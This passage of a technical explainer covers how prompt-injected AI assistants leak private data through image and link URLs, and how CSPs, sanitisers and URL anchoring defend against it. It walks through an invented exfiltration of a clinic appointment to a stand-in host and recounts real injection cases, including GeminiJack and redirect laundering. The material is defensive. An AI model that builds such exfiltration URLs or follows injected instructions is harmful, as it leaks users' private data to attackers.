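# Limiting where AI assistants can send data: content security policies and URL anchoring

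## How an assistant can leak data through a web address

AI assistants such as Microsoft Copilot, Google Gemini, ChatGPT and Claude are built on language models, and many can read a user's mail and files or look things up on the web. This exposes them to text written by strangers, some of whom write it to take control of the assistant. These attackers often aim for exfiltration, the transfer of private data to someone not entitled to it. One of the easiest methods is to get the assistant to compose a web address that points to the attacker's server and contains the private data. When any computer requests that address, the server receives the data.

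Vendors respond by restricting which addresses the assistant, its tools and the user's browser may request. A web page can send the browser a content security policy (CSP), which lists the sources from which the page may load images, scripts and other resources. A sanitiser is code that removes or disables risky elements, such as external images, in the assistant's answer. Other rules limit which pages the assistant may open on its own, and network limits restrict the programs it runs. Many of these restrictions use an allowlist, which permits only the destinations on it. The restrictions make it harder for a fooled model to send data out, but they don't make the model harder to fool.

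### Instructions hidden in content

A language model takes in one continuous run of text. When a user asks for a summary of a web page, the assistant joins the vendor's standing instructions, the user's request and the text of the page, and hands all of it to the model together. Vendors can put markers between the parts, but the model has no dependable way of telling an order from the user apart from a sentence on the page that reads like one. Indirect prompt injection exploits this: someone hides instructions in content that the assistant will read, and the model follows them as if the user had given them. (In a direct injection the attacker is the user, typing into the chat.)

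Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023), in *Not what you've signed up for*, introduced the concept of indirect prompt injection and compared a model processing retrieved text to a computer running code from an unknown source. They tested it on Bing Chat, the assistant in Microsoft's search engine, whose sidebar in the Edge browser could read the page the user had open. Instructions on the page steered the model even when a human visitor could not see them. An attacker can also put instructions in other content, even a plain text file. Greshake and colleagues list emails, imported code, images and text that a user copies from a malicious site, and Microsoft, in a 2025 account of its own defences, adds shared documents and the data that tools return.

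An injection may do little harm on its own, such as when a hidden line makes an assistant end every summary with a joke. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, the software developer Simon Willison (2025) set out three conditions for data theft: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and some means of communicating with the outside world. Removing any one of these prevents the theft.

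A single tool can meet more than one of the three conditions. A mailbox holds private data, and any stranger can put text in it, so an assistant that reads mail meets two of the conditions without opening a web page. The third, a way to send data out, is easy to add by accident. Willison counts API requests, image loading, and even links that the user might click, none of which looks much like sending a message.

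### What a web address carries

Take an invented address (the technical name is URL, for uniform resource locator):

`https://pictures.example/dot.png?note=clinic-tuesday-0900`

The opening `https` names the protocol. The host, `pictures.example`, determines which server receives the request. `/dot.png` is the path, and everything after the question mark is the query, a set of named values that the server's owner can use as they like. In the early days of the web, the path was the location of a file, but Mozilla's *What is a URL?* describes it as mostly an abstraction today. So whoever runs `pictures.example` can return the same picture for every path and query, and can record any text they contain. Text after a `#` sign would not reach the server, because browsers do not send it.

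To load the address, a browser finds the server for that host and sends it the path and the query. Web servers commonly write each request to a log. *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT*, a 2023 post on security researcher Johann Rehberger's blog, Embrace The Red, shows a real log line. It contains the date and time, the path and query, a response code and the browser's description of itself, and the query holds a complete link that ChatGPT had leaked. In the invented case, the log would hold "clinic-tuesday-0900". The server's reply, whether a picture, a blank page or an error message, makes no difference because the server has already received the data.

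HTTPS does not prevent this kind of leak, because it hides the path and query from eavesdroppers but delivers them in readable form to the receiving server. OWASP's *Information exposure through query strings in url*, a reference page from a web-security foundation, lists web logs among the places where query values appear with or without HTTPS. MITRE's *CWE-598*, an entry in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, gives the usual remedy for honest websites, which is to send sensitive values in a POST request and keep them out of the address. This protects users from careless sites, but in an exfiltration the site's owner wants the data in the log and chose the form of the address for that purpose.

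Microsoft notes that an attacker can also put the data in the path or in a subdomain (an extra label in front of the host name) instead of the query, and can encode it, for example in base64, which turns text into an unreadable string of characters. A filter that scanned addresses for names or telephone numbers would miss data encoded this way.

### One leak from start to finish

Suppose a user has connected an assistant to a mailbox and wants to arrange a lunch.

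1. The attacker publishes a page of restaurant reviews with an extra paragraph in white letters on a white background. The paragraph asks for the reader's next appointment, and for a picture whose address contains it.
2. The user asks the assistant to choose a restaurant from the page that fits next week's plans. The assistant fetches the page and looks through the mailbox, so the hidden paragraph and a clinic's confirmation end up in the same input.
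3. The model writes a recommendation. Below it, in line with the hidden paragraph, it adds an image in Markdown, a plain-text notation that chat software converts into headings, links and pictures. The image's address is the invented one above.
4. The user's browser receives the answer, finds an image to display and requests it from `pictures.example`.
5. The server logs the appointment and returns a transparent picture one pixel wide. The user sees a restaurant recommendation.

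The model only produced text. Ordinary web software contacted the attacker when it treated part of that text as something to load. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out that a forced request leaks data even when the chat shows nothing sensitive, and that the user may never notice a request made in the background.

### The image leaks of 2023

Two researchers found almost exactly this leak in real products in spring 2023. SecurityWeek's *Malicious GPT Can Phish Credentials, Exfiltrate Them to External Server* reports that they found it independently. One of them, the software engineer Roman Samoilenko, described an attack that used copy and paste in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*. A script on a malicious website added instructions to any text a visitor copied. When the visitor pasted the text into ChatGPT, the model added an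 invisible one-pixel image to its answer and put material from the chat in the image's address. The instructions could make the model do the same in every later answer in the session.

Samoilenko noted that the same text might work on one attempt and fail on the next because the model's output varies. It was fairly easy to extract the user's previous question or a piece of code, but very difficult to extract passwords and keys. Samoilenko still advised OpenAI to stop showing Markdown images in ChatGPT's answers.

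Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* describes Rehberger's demonstration of an attack that didn't require the user to paste anything. The instructions were on a web page that the user was discussing with the assistant. Bing Chat came under their control immediately, but it was instructed to wait two exchanges before adding an image to its answer. The image's address contained an encoded summary of the page and the conversation, along with a secret from elsewhere on the page. Anyone who could post a comment or place an advertisement on a page could therefore steal whatever else that page showed to the user.

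Rehberger reported the problem to Microsoft on 8 April 2023 and to OpenAI a day later. On 15 June, Rehberger heard that Microsoft's fix, apparently built around a content security policy, was in place. Rehberger recounts in *ChatGPT Plugins* that OpenAI replied that displaying such images was a feature and that it planned no change. OpenAI didn't introduce a first, partial check until December 2023. Rehberger examined that check in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*.

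By the end of the following year, Rehberger had found and reported the flaw in eleven products listed in *Trust No AI* (2024), including Claude, Google Bard, Discord and GitHub Copilot Chat. *HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data*, by the security firm PromptArmor, describes the same flaw in HuggingChat, a chat application from the AI company Hugging Face. PromptArmor reported it to Hugging Face on 1 December 2025 and went public after getting no response. The flaw probably keeps recurring because it needs only common features. Any chat page has it if the page displays Markdown images from anywhere on the web and the model behind it reads both private data and strangers' text.

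### Who sends the request, and whether anyone clicks

In the image leaks, the user's browser sent the request, so a rule that the browser enforces could stop it. Other machines also send requests, and such a rule does not apply to those requests.

Assistants often open web pages through a server-side fetch, in which the vendor's server requests the address. A content security policy on the chat page can't block this fetch because the request doesn't go through the user's browser. The vendor has to check the address before its server connects.

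Other companies' services may also send the request. *Let ChatGPT visit a website and have your email stolen* (Willison, 2023) describes a demonstration by Rehberger with ChatGPT plugins, the add-ons that let ChatGPT use outside services at the time. The WebPilot plugin retrieved a page with hidden instructions, the Zapier plugin fetched the latest email from Gmail, and WebPilot then requested an address to which the model had appended a short encoded summary of that email. Messaging apps can also send the request, without any plugin. Rehberger explains that Slack, Discord, Teams and similar apps automatically connect to links in a conversation to show a preview of the page. If an assistant posted the link, the preview request delivers whatever the link contains to the attacker, without the assistant's vendor or the user's browser sending the attacker anything.

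An automatic fetch is a request sent without the user clicking anything, whichever machine sends it. Attacks that rely on automatic fetches are zero-click, because the victim only has to ask an ordinary question for the data to leak. A one-click attack requires the victim to follow a link. Samoilenko demonstrated this variant as well, with a link that contained code from the conversation.

Having to click a link gives a person a chance to look at the address first, but this is a weak safeguard. Markdown can show the words "click here" in place of the address, and encoded data looks much like the random-looking text at the end of many legitimate links. Whether a leak requires a click also depends on the software around the assistant. PromptArmor describes how an assistant's malicious link can leak data automatically in a messaging app with previews enabled, whereas without previews the user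 would typically have to click it.

### Why designers guard the exit as well as the input

Vendors put a good deal of work into stopping the model from obeying instructions in external text. Microsoft's Spotlighting method marks such text, for example with a special character between all its words, and tells the model not to follow instructions in the marked text. Its Prompt Shields product is a classifier, a program trained on known attacks to flag new ones. Microsoft calls such defences probabilistic, meaning that they make attacks less likely but may not prevent or detect every one. A deterministic defence guarantees, through the design of the system, that a particular attack will fail even though the model remains unpredictable. For example, a browser can refuse every image from outside an allowlist. Clever wording in the hidden text doesn't help the attacker, because the browser never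 interprets it.

Microsoft prefers deterministic defences where possible, but considers deterministic detection of injections an open research problem. It therefore designs its products assuming that some injections will succeed, and tries to keep those from doing damage. Similarly, software engineers try to avoid memory errors, but also build in protections to keep any that remain from leading to a break-in.

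A few words can change how well the probabilistic defences work. *The Framing Gap* (2026) reports experiments in which a confidentiality policy that forbade disclosure "in any form" cut leaks from 31.9% to zero. When the policy named specific behaviours but lacked the general clause, the leak rate was 48.8%. A separate detector whose only task was to recognise injections caught every variant without a false alarm.

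Commercial products can also resist injection attacks well. In *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, Willison discusses an evaluation that Anthropic commissioned of its programming assistant, Claude Code, in versions available in July 2026. The testers made 720 injection attempts against three Claude models running in auto mode, where the user doesn't have to approve each action, and none succeeded.

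The defences behind these strong results make attacks rarer, but the tests cover only attacks that someone thought to try. Even if the 720 attempts were a fair random sample, zero successes would be compatible, at the usual 95% confidence, with a true success rate as high as about one in 240. Real attackers instead vary the wording until something works and then reuse it on everyone, which is why Willison regards a product that catches 95% of attacks as a failure by the standards of web security. Willison also describes an attack that might get past even a very good filter, in which a software package's documentation asks for a routine set-up step and the set-up program itself sends out the data.

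If injections cannot be ruled out, preventing theft means removing one of its three conditions. Private data is the reason people connect an assistant to their mail, and an assistant that read nothing from strangers could not search the web or summarise an incoming message. Willison concludes that the ability to send data out is generally the easiest condition to remove, and vendors who patched leaks of this kind have usually done so by restricting that ability. A hidden instruction can still make a summary false, however, and a deterministic rule blocks only the route it covers.

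The simplest way to limit where an assistant can send data is an allowlist of trusted sites, but people want assistants to read far more of the web than such a list could cover. URL anchoring instead restricts addresses based on where they came from. An assistant may automatically open an address only if it came from a source other than the assistant's own writing, such as the user's message, search results or a public index, which is a record of addresses that a crawler found without access to any user's data. "URL anchoring" is a descriptive label, and vendors use names such as "Safe Url". In the restaurant example, the model composed the address itself, partly from an email. The user had not typed it, no search had returned it, and a crawler was very unlikely to have found it, so software that applied the rule to images would not have loaded this one.

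## How a content security policy restricts what the browser loads

In the restaurant example, the user's browser fetched the attacker's image because browsers load images from any host unless the page's server restricts them. Servers usually do this with a content security policy. *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current working draft from the web standards consortium W3C, defines how a server writes such a policy and how a browser applies it. These policies mainly protect against cross-site scripting, in which an attacker inserts their own script into someone else's page. W3C recommends them as a second layer of defence, behind careful checks on what goes into the page.

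A chat page has a similar problem, since a stranger's hidden instructions can affect what appears on it. A content security policy can block images from outside sources, just as it blocks scripts.

### Directives and sources

The server sends the policy in a header, one of several lines of settings that arrive ahead of the page. (A developer can also write the policy into the page's own code, but then it doesn't apply to anything that comes earlier in the page.) Suppose a vendor serves its chat page from `chat.example` and keeps generated images on servers under `chatcdn.example`. A short policy might read:

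```
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self'; img-src 'self' https://*.chatcdn.example; form-action 'self'
```

Semicolons separate the directives. Each directive has a name, which determines the kind of request it governs, and a list of permitted sources. `'self'` permits the page's own origin (the same protocol, host and port), `'none'` permits nothing, and `*.` in front of a host permits its subdomains. If a directive appears twice in one policy, the browser ignores the second copy, so adding a stricter `img-src` after an existing one has no effect.

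These directives matter most for a chat page:

| Directive | What it governs | If the policy omits it |
|---|---|---|
| `default-src` | Every type of loading that has no directive of its own in the policy | Those types have no limit |
| `img-src` | Images | `default-src` applies |
| `style-src` | Style sheets, and styles written into the page itself | `default-src` applies |
| `font-src` | Web fonts | `default-src` applies |
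| `connect-src` | Connections that scripts open to send or receive data | `default-src` applies |
| `frame-src` | Other pages displayed in a frame inside this one | `child-src` applies, then `default-src` |
| `form-action` | Where the page may submit a form | Forms can go to any server |

The browser first checks what each request is for. An image request falls under `img-src`, or under `default-src` if the policy has no `img-src`. If the policy has neither, the browser allows the request. Otherwise, it compares the address with each source in the directive's list and allows the request if any source matches. If none matches, the page gets a network error and the browser never contacts the server.

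A specific directive replaces the default for its type and inherits nothing from it. The example therefore repeats `'self'` under `img-src` so that the chat page can load its own logo. The last row of the table covers a gap that is easy to overlook, since even a policy of `default-src 'none'` lets a page submit forms anywhere.

### Four requests tested against the policy

In the restaurant example, the model's answer includes an image at `https://pictures.example/dot.png?note=clinic-tuesday-0900`. The browser blocks the request for this image because `pictures.example` is neither the page's own origin nor a subdomain of `chatcdn.example`. The user may see a broken-image icon, but no request reaches the attacker's server.

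Suppose the answer contains a chart at `https://eu.chatcdn.example/chart.png`. The protocol is right and the host ends in `.chatcdn.example`, so the chart loads. `a.b.chatcdn.example` would also pass, because the asterisk covers subdomains at any depth, but the bare `chatcdn.example` would not. The chart would still load with `?note=clinic-tuesday-0900` added to the end of its URL. The browser compares the protocol, the host, the port and, if the policy gives one, the path. It doesn't compare the query, and W3C's syntax has no way to restrict it. A policy therefore limits which hosts can receive data, but the query can carry any data to an allowed host.

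Style sheets can also request images, such as the background of a button. W3C describes attacks in which a style rule loads a background image only if some value in the page's code begins with a particular letter, so the requests reveal the value without any script. The example policy allows the chat page's own style sheet because it comes from `'self'`. If that style sheet requests a background image from `pictures.example`, the browser checks the request against `img-src` and blocks it. The browser would ignore a style rule that the model wrote straight into the answer, because a `style-src` or `default-src` list blocks styles written into the page unless the developer explicitly allows them.

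In the last case, the browser requests an image from `eu.chatcdn.example`, and the server replies with a redirect (an instruction to fetch a different address) to `pictures.example`. The browser allows the first request but checks the new address before following the redirect. Because `pictures.example` isn't on the list, the browser blocks the second request. The attacker's server receives nothing, although `eu.chatcdn.example` has already received whatever the first address contained.

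### Redirects and paths

A filter on the vendor's server that checked only the first domain in each address in the answer would have approved that last image. It would have checked `eu.chatcdn.example` but not `pictures.example`, which appears only in the redirect that `eu.chatcdn.example` sends back. Report URI's *Connection Allowlist*, a post from a company that monitors browser policies, calls this trick "redirect laundering". The browser follows the redirects itself, so it can check every address along the way.

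The check after a redirect is slightly looser than the first one. A source in a policy can include a path. A path that ends in a slash permits everything beneath it, and any other path permits only an exact match. After a redirect, the browser still compares the protocol, host and port but ignores the path.

Suppose the vendor adds `https://files.example/logos/` to `img-src`. A direct request for an image in `files.example/uploads/` fails because the path doesn't match. If a server under `chatcdn.example` redirects the browser to the same image, the request succeeds.

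W3C made this exception to protect other sites. Otherwise, a malicious page could write a policy naming one path on another site, load an address that redirects there, and see whether the browser blocked it. By trying one path after another, the page could work out where the other site redirects a particular visitor, which might be private information.

Browser makers test for this behaviour. A Mozilla test checks that Firefox blocks a script requested from the wrong path but loads one that is redirected to a wrong path. WebKit, the engine in Apple's Safari, passes similar tests for images, frames and style sheets. A vendor therefore can't rely on a path to keep the browser to the safe part of a shared host if an attacker can get any permitted host to redirect to the rest of it.

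The redirect check also doesn't control what a permitted server does with the data it receives. The server can forward the data over its own connection or store it where the attacker can collect it.

### How one loose entry undoes a policy

The W3C draft has a short section on exfiltration, with two examples of policies that look strict but are not. The first bans all images, scripts and fonts but has no `default-src`, so data can still leave through other kinds of request, such as a prefetch, in which the browser loads something early because the user may need it soon. Prefetching has no directive of its own, so only a policy with a `default-src` can limit it. Even then, the browser allows prefetches to any server listed in any of the policy's loading directives, so a host permitted for fonts can also receive prefetches.

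The second example is `default-src 'none'; img-src *`. The asterisk allows images from anywhere, and an image request can carry data just as any other request can. W3C concludes that a policy protects against exfiltration only as well as its least restrictive list.

Adding a second policy can't loosen the first, because a request has to satisfy both. A frame whose contents are supplied in the answer itself inherits the chat page's policy, so putting an image inside one doesn't bypass the restrictions. But a frame that loads a page from another server uses that page's own policy, if it has one, and can load images that the chat page could not. Developers therefore need to choose the hosts in `frame-src` as carefully as those in `img-src`.

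### Testing a policy before enforcing it

A large site may load images, fonts and scripts from dozens of hosts, and a policy that omits one of them breaks part of the page. Developers can test a policy by sending it in the `Content-Security-Policy-Report-Only` header. The browser then loads everything as before, but sends a report to an address the developer has chosen whenever the policy would have blocked a request. W3C suggests starting with a best guess at what the site needs, watching the reports and enforcing the policy once they show nothing unexpected. A server can send this header alongside `Content-Security-Policy` to enforce its current policy while testing a stricter one.

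Report-only mode doesn't prevent leaks. If the restaurant image appeared during the trial, the browser would report it to the vendor but still load it, which would send the appointment to the attacker.

That report can contain private data too. Under W3C's rules, the browser removes any username, password and text after a `#` from the blocked address but keeps the query, so the report would contain "clinic-tuesday-0900". A vendor that has an outside company collect its reports would share its users' data with that company. If a redirect caused the violation, the report gives only the address the page originally requested, because the target's address might contain details of the visitor's login. W3C also warns developers to treat reports as text an attacker may have written.

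### Microsoft's fix for Bing Chat

Microsoft's June 2023 fix for the Bing Chat image leak was an early test of this method on an AI assistant. When Rehberger repeated the attack, it no longer worked. Embrace The Red reports that the page now had a policy that permitted images from four hosts: `th.bing.com`, `www.bing.com`, `edgeservices.bing.com` and `r.bing.com`. Microsoft could not ban all images because Bing Chat could create pictures on request.

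Rehberger credited the policy with only part of the fix because Microsoft might have made other changes that outsiders could not see. According to Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* (2026), Microsoft was the first vendor to acknowledge and address the flaw, and many others followed with their own fixes.

Microsoft later used a more elaborate set of restrictions for the Copilot sidebar in its Edge browser. Kokatsu's conference slides, *Piloting Edge Copilot*, list separate allowlists for frames, script connections, images, style sheets and media, with `'self'` for everything else. Edge also requires the page inside the sidebar's frame to accept a minimum policy, because a framed page otherwise sets its own policy.

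Outsiders can inspect a policy because the server sends it to every visitor. Embrace The Red contrasts this with OpenAI's first check in ChatGPT, whose exact rules Rehberger could only guess at. Attackers can also read the policy and search the permitted hosts for a relay. Willison (2026), in *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, blames one such leak on a policy that permitted images from `docs.google.com`. That domain also hosts Google Forms, which stores data sent to it as part of a web address. The EchoLeak and SearchLeak attacks succeeded against Microsoft 365 Copilot, Microsoft's assistant for businesses, despite several layers of defence.

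### Clicks and other requests outside the policy

When a user clicks an ordinary link, the browser leaves the page for another one. W3C calls this a navigation, and no directive in the 2026 draft lets a developer list the permitted destinations for such links. `form-action` covers only form submissions. `connect-src` covers the background message, called a ping, that some links send when clicked, but not the navigation itself. If the model in the restaurant example had written a link instead of an image, the policy would not have stopped a user's click from sending out the appointment.

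W3C's working group did plan a directive for this, called `navigate-to`, but removed it from the specification in September 2022. According to Mozilla's bug tracker, no browser ever shipped it. CentralCSP's *navigate-to*, a page from a company that sells policy tools, explains that the group never settled how to treat redirects and navigation to other sites. A malicious page could also have used the directive to find out whether a visitor was logged in to another site. Chrome's developers had kept an unfinished version behind a test setting and later deleted it, as web-platform-tests' *[CSP] Remove code for navigate-to* records.

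Chrome now has a separate mechanism with wider coverage. Chrome (2026) lists Connection Allowlists among the new features of version 152, which came out on 25 August 2026. A server sends one list of address patterns in a header of its own, and the browser refuses every connection from the page that doesn't match, whatever its type:

```
Connection-Allowlist: (response-origin "https://*.chatcdn.example")
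```

The draft specification *Connection Allowlists* uses `response-origin` where a content security policy uses `'self'`. In it, West, a Google engineer who also edits the content security policy standard, argues that separate lists for images, fonts and scripts make little sense against exfiltration, because a leak through a font request is as bad as a leak through an image request. West adds that the older standard's coverage is incomplete. For example, it fits poorly with direct connections between browsers and with early lookups of host names, which can leak data without loading anything because the name itself may contain the data.

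Chrome's *Connection Allowlists origin trial* (2026), which announced the feature's public test, gives AI-generated code as a main reason for the feature. Such code may send data to unintended places, and a site that runs it can use the allowlist to contain it. The announcement also says the feature covers navigations. Chromestatus's *Intent to Experiment* (2026) gives a longer list of what the feature covers, including navigations and the back and forward buttons. Clicks on links seem to count as navigations, though the list doesn't mention them.

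The treatment of redirects was still changing during development. West's draft blocks every redirect, but West doubted that this would be practical for real sites and suggested alternatives, including checking each step as a content security policy does. According to Chrome's announcement, the browser checks the redirect's destination against the list.

Report URI describes the new header as limited to Chrome 152 and other browsers built on the same code, though it expects the rest to follow. In March 2026 the makers of Firefox and Safari had not indicated whether they would adopt it. An assistant that cites its sources has to let users open links to almost any site, so its vendor can hardly list the permitted destinations in advance. The header works better for a small tool that displays a chart or runs generated code, because such a tool doesn't need to link to so many sites.

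Neither header affects a server-side fetch, because the request doesn't go through the user's browser. W3C also asks browsers not to let a page's policy interfere with user-installed extensions, so a vendor can't use its chat page's policy to restrict what an extension sends.

### Apps inside ChatGPT

ChatGPT can show small apps from other companies, such as forms or interactive charts, in a conversation. Developers build them with the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open specification for connecting assistants to outside tools. OpenAI's *app security whitepaper* calls the visible part of an app a widget and says it runs in a sandbox that OpenAI controls. According to OpenAI's *MCP Apps in ChatGPT*, the widget sits in a frame, a separate page embedded in the main one, and exchanges messages with ChatGPT through a defined channel.

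A third-party app's code needs a separate frame in ChatGPT, according to notes on a conference talk by Barthelet (AI Engineer, 2026). ChatGPT's own policy blocks unknown scripts, so an app placed directly in the chat page would not run. If that policy were relaxed, the app would run, but it could also read everything that ChatGPT's own scripts can, including data stored in the browser, and send it to the app's maker. A frame with its own origin keeps the app away from that data, and a separate policy for the frame limits where the app can connect.

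The developer supplies the list of domains for that policy. mcp-use's *Content Security Policy*, the documentation of a software library for building such apps, describes the main fields:

- `connectDomains` lists the servers that the app's scripts may contact, as `connect-src` does.
- `resourceDomains` lists the hosts for scripts, style sheets and images, and also covers fonts and media.
- `frameDomains` lists the sites that the app may show in frames of its own.
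- `redirectDomains` exists only in ChatGPT and concerns links that take the user out of the app.

ChatGPT also accepts an older notation with underscores, such as `connect_domains`. In *Trouble with CSP after publishing dev app*, a thread on OpenAI's developer forum, rlittl asked for help with an app that kept having a request blocked. Another user replied that developers must declare their domains before they distribute an app widely, and that the sandbox blocks everything else.

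The single field for resources is easy to fill in, but it may allow more than the developer intended, because a host listed for its fonts can also supply images and even scripts. The lists also protect users only from third parties. If hostile text gets into a restaurant-booking app, the browser won't let the app send the booking to a server the developer never declared. But the developer's own server is on the list and can receive anything the app has access to.

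The frame's policy doesn't govern clicks, so ChatGPT handles links in apps separately. In *Verifying URLs used in apps*, another forum thread, a developer complained that users saw a warning whenever they followed a link from the app to the developer's own website, while some large companies' apps showed none. The reply recommended declaring the website under `redirect_domains`.

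## Removing images and links from the answer before it is shown

A content security policy takes effect when the browser is about to send a request, but a sanitiser edits the answer before it reaches the page. If the sanitiser removes the restaurant image, the browser never requests it. The sanitiser can also remove links, which a content security policy doesn't control.

### From Markdown to a request

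Chat software turns the model's text into part of a web page in several steps. Suppose an answer contains an image in the usual Markdown notation:

```
![Our logo](https://pictures.example/logo.png)
```

A parser reads the text and builds a tree from it, in which a paragraph contains an image and the image has an address. A renderer writes the tree as HTML, the language of web pages, where the image becomes an `<img>` tag. The chat page inserts this HTML, and the browser then accesses the image's address, as ainoya.dev's *Rendering Markdown Images in LLM Apps?* explains. A sanitiser can work on the original text, the tree or the finished HTML.

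The simplest sanitisers search the text for a pattern, such as an exclamation mark followed by square brackets and an address in parentheses, and delete whatever matches. This pattern would find the logo above but not the same logo in reference style, which puts the address on a line of its own:

```
![Our logo][pic]

[pic]: https://pictures.example/logo.png
```

Many Markdown programs also accept HTML, so the model can write the `<img>` tag directly. A developer can add a pattern for each of these forms, but there are many smaller variations, such as a title after the address or character codes in place of letters. Patterns can also damage harmless answers. A user who asks how Markdown images work needs to see the notation, which loads nothing inside a code block.

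Attackers know about these gaps. 0din, a site that publishes research on AI vulnerabilities, describes an attack on Google's programming tool Antigravity in which the hidden instructions asked for the same image in five notations, including an HTML tag, an HTML figure and reference-style Markdown, and only one had to load for the attack to work. In Google AI Studio, a site where developers try out Google's models, Rehberger found that Markdown tricks worked only sporadically, but asking the model for an HTML image tag worked, according to Embrace The Red's *Google AI Studio*. AI Studio had no content security policy at the time to stop the resulting request. Google fixed the leak quickly.

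A sanitiser that works on the parsed tree avoids most of this trouble, because the parser has already interpreted the notation. Both versions of the logo become the same kind of image in the tree, so one rule removes both, and sample code stays intact. Raw HTML is the exception, because Markdown parsers usually copy it into the output without interpreting it. The developer has to discard it or clean it at the next stage.

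Before the answer is shown, a sanitiser parses its HTML much as a browser would and checks each element and attribute. The safest version keeps only what is on an approved list, such as headings, paragraphs, tables and bold text. If the developer forgets to list an element, the answer loses some formatting, whereas forgetting one on a list of forbidden elements can leak data.

### Filtering before display

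Assistants usually show an answer while the model is still writing it. If the page displays each piece as it arrives and the sanitiser checks only the finished answer, the browser may request an image seconds before the sanitiser deletes it. The finished answer then shows no image, even though the attacker's server already has the data.

The sanitiser therefore has to process every partial answer before the page displays it. Reference-style images make this harder. In the second example, the first line is ordinary text until the line with the address arrives and the parser turns it into an image. A sanitiser that checked each line only once would let both lines through. It has to parse the whole answer again as it grows, or hold back any text that might still become an image.

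A sanitiser can itself trigger a request. When a script in a web page creates an `<img>` element, the browser may start loading the image even if the element isn't attached to anything visible. Careful sanitisers avoid this by parsing the HTML in a separate, inactive document, where images don't load.

The sanitiser should run last, because later steps can create elements that it did not check. For example, chat software may turn bare addresses into links, draw diagrams from a text description or colour sample code. Filter failures also contributed to the EchoLeak and SearchLeak attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot.

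### Gemini's image and link filters

Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (June 2025) describes the filters for the Gemini app and the Gemini features in Google Workspace, the company's set of office programs. Before the model answers, classifiers look for malicious instructions in emails and files, and extra text around the content reminds the model to stick to the user's task. A Markdown sanitiser then finds external images in the answer and doesn't display them. Google concluded that the image leak in EchoLeak did not apply to Gemini.

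Gemini is more selective with links, removing only those it classifies as suspicious. In Google's example, a user asks Gemini in Gmail to summarise an email thread that contains an unsafe URL, and the summary shows "suspicious link removed" in place of the URL.

Google bases this judgement on Safe Browsing, its service for identifying dangerous websites, which also provides the warnings in Chrome. Safe Browsing works well against known phishing sites, but it rates the destination rather than the contents of the address, which is where the leaked data is. An attacker who only wants to collect that data needs a server that keeps a log, not malware or a false login page. *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents*, by the software security company Checkmarx, points out that Safe Browsing has to recognise a site as malicious before Gemini can remove its links, so a newly registered domain can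 pass.

*Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* (Gavish, 2026), a newer post by a member of Google's security team, explains how the company keeps these defences up to date. It classes URL sanitisation as a deterministic defence, along with user confirmation and rules on which tools the assistant may use in sequence. Google keeps the settings for all of these in a central policy engine. When a new attack appears, Google can change a setting or block a text pattern much faster than it can retrain a model. Blocking a pattern can stop an attack that Google has already seen, but an attacker can look for a variation that the pattern misses, whereas the rule against external images needs no update when the attacker's wording changes.

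Gavish adds that Google measures the effect of a defence by simulating attacks on Gmail, Docs and other applications with it switched on and then off. The post gives no results for URL sanitisation, and neither post gives a criterion for suspicious links other than Safe Browsing. According to Embrace The Red, Google also uses its search index to recognise public addresses, which is a form of URL anchoring.

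Conference Intel's *Securing Workspace GenAI at Google Speed* (2026) summarises a talk by Nicolas Lidzborski, a Google engineer who has spent three years securing Gemini in Workspace. Lidzborski argued that defenders can't beat prompt injection by filtering prompts, and described a four-layer design with output sanitisation as the last layer.

The security company Tenable tested Gemini and found that it filtered or restricted images and links, cut off suspicious answers and sometimes refused to respond. Tenable therefore tried to get data out through Gemini's tools, whose requests don't depend on what the answer displays.

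Another researcher did get past the sanitiser, according to Adversa AI's *Google Workspace Gemini Agent Security Risks*, a risk profile that draws on published research. The researcher combined quirks in linkification, the automatic conversion of text into links, with open redirects, which are pages on trusted sites that forward visitors to any address named in the link. Together these made an image load automatically and carry Workspace data to an outside server. Google paid the researcher through its reward programme. Although Google's rule was simple, the code that enforced it still had to interpret every address correctly.

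### GeminiJack

Gemini Enterprise, a separate Google product for large organisations, had no such protection when the security company Noma tested it in 2025. It answers questions by searching a company's emails, calendars and documents and adding the best matches to the model's input, a method known as retrieval-augmented generation. An attacker could hide instructions in a document about budgets and share it with someone in the company. When an employee later asked Gemini Enterprise about budgets, the search found the document and the model followed the instructions, even if the victim had never opened it.

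Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Fixes Zero Click Gemini Enterprise Flaw That Exposed Corporate Data* reports that Gemini then searched the company's data for sensitive terms and added an image tag to its answer, with the results in the image's address. When the employee's browser loaded the image, it sent the results to the attacker. Noma named the attack GeminiJack.

Noma's research lead, Sasi Levi, said in TechFinitive's *GeminiJack zero-click vulnerability exposes dangerous underbelly of the AI revolution* that "Google didn't filter HTML output". In TechNadu's *New AI-Native Threat*, Levi said Noma had not measured the maximum amount of data per request but had extracted lengthy emails. Many sensitive documents are no longer than a lengthy email.

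Reports differ on when Noma told Google about GeminiJack. TechNadu gives 6 May 2025 and SecurityWeek's *Google Patches Gemini Enterprise Vulnerability Exposing Corporate Data* also gives May, but Infosecurity Magazine gives June. Either way, Google published its account of Gemini's image filter before it had fixed GeminiJack. The post covered only the Gemini app and Workspace, so GeminiJack didn't contradict it. A sanitiser protects only the products that run it, so a company with many assistants has to install it in each one.

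Google fixed the flaw by November 2025 and confirmed to SecurityWeek that Noma's description was accurate. It changed how Gemini Enterprise and Vertex AI Search, a related product, worked with the systems that retrieve and index documents. It also separated the two products, and Vertex AI Search stopped using the same model-driven process. According to Noma, the fix addressed the confusion between instructions and content.

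It is unclear whether Google also began to filter the HTML. In SC Media's *Google addresses ‘GeminiJack’ exploit affecting Gemini Enterprise*, Levi said that Google had not disclosed the technical details and that Noma didn't know whether the fix included sanitising. This matters because only an HTML filter would still block the image after a successful injection.

### Checkmarx's tests of Copilot Chat and Gemini

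Checkmarx reported problems in Microsoft Copilot Chat and Gemini to their makers in October 2025. It described both as vulnerable to Markdown injection, but the two leaks were different.

Checkmarx demonstrated a zero-click leak in Copilot Chat. The assistant read an online article with hidden instructions and added an image to its answer. The image's address contained a secret key from the developer's environment. (Checkmarx had already cancelled the key.) No picture appeared in the chat, but the request still reached Checkmarx's server.

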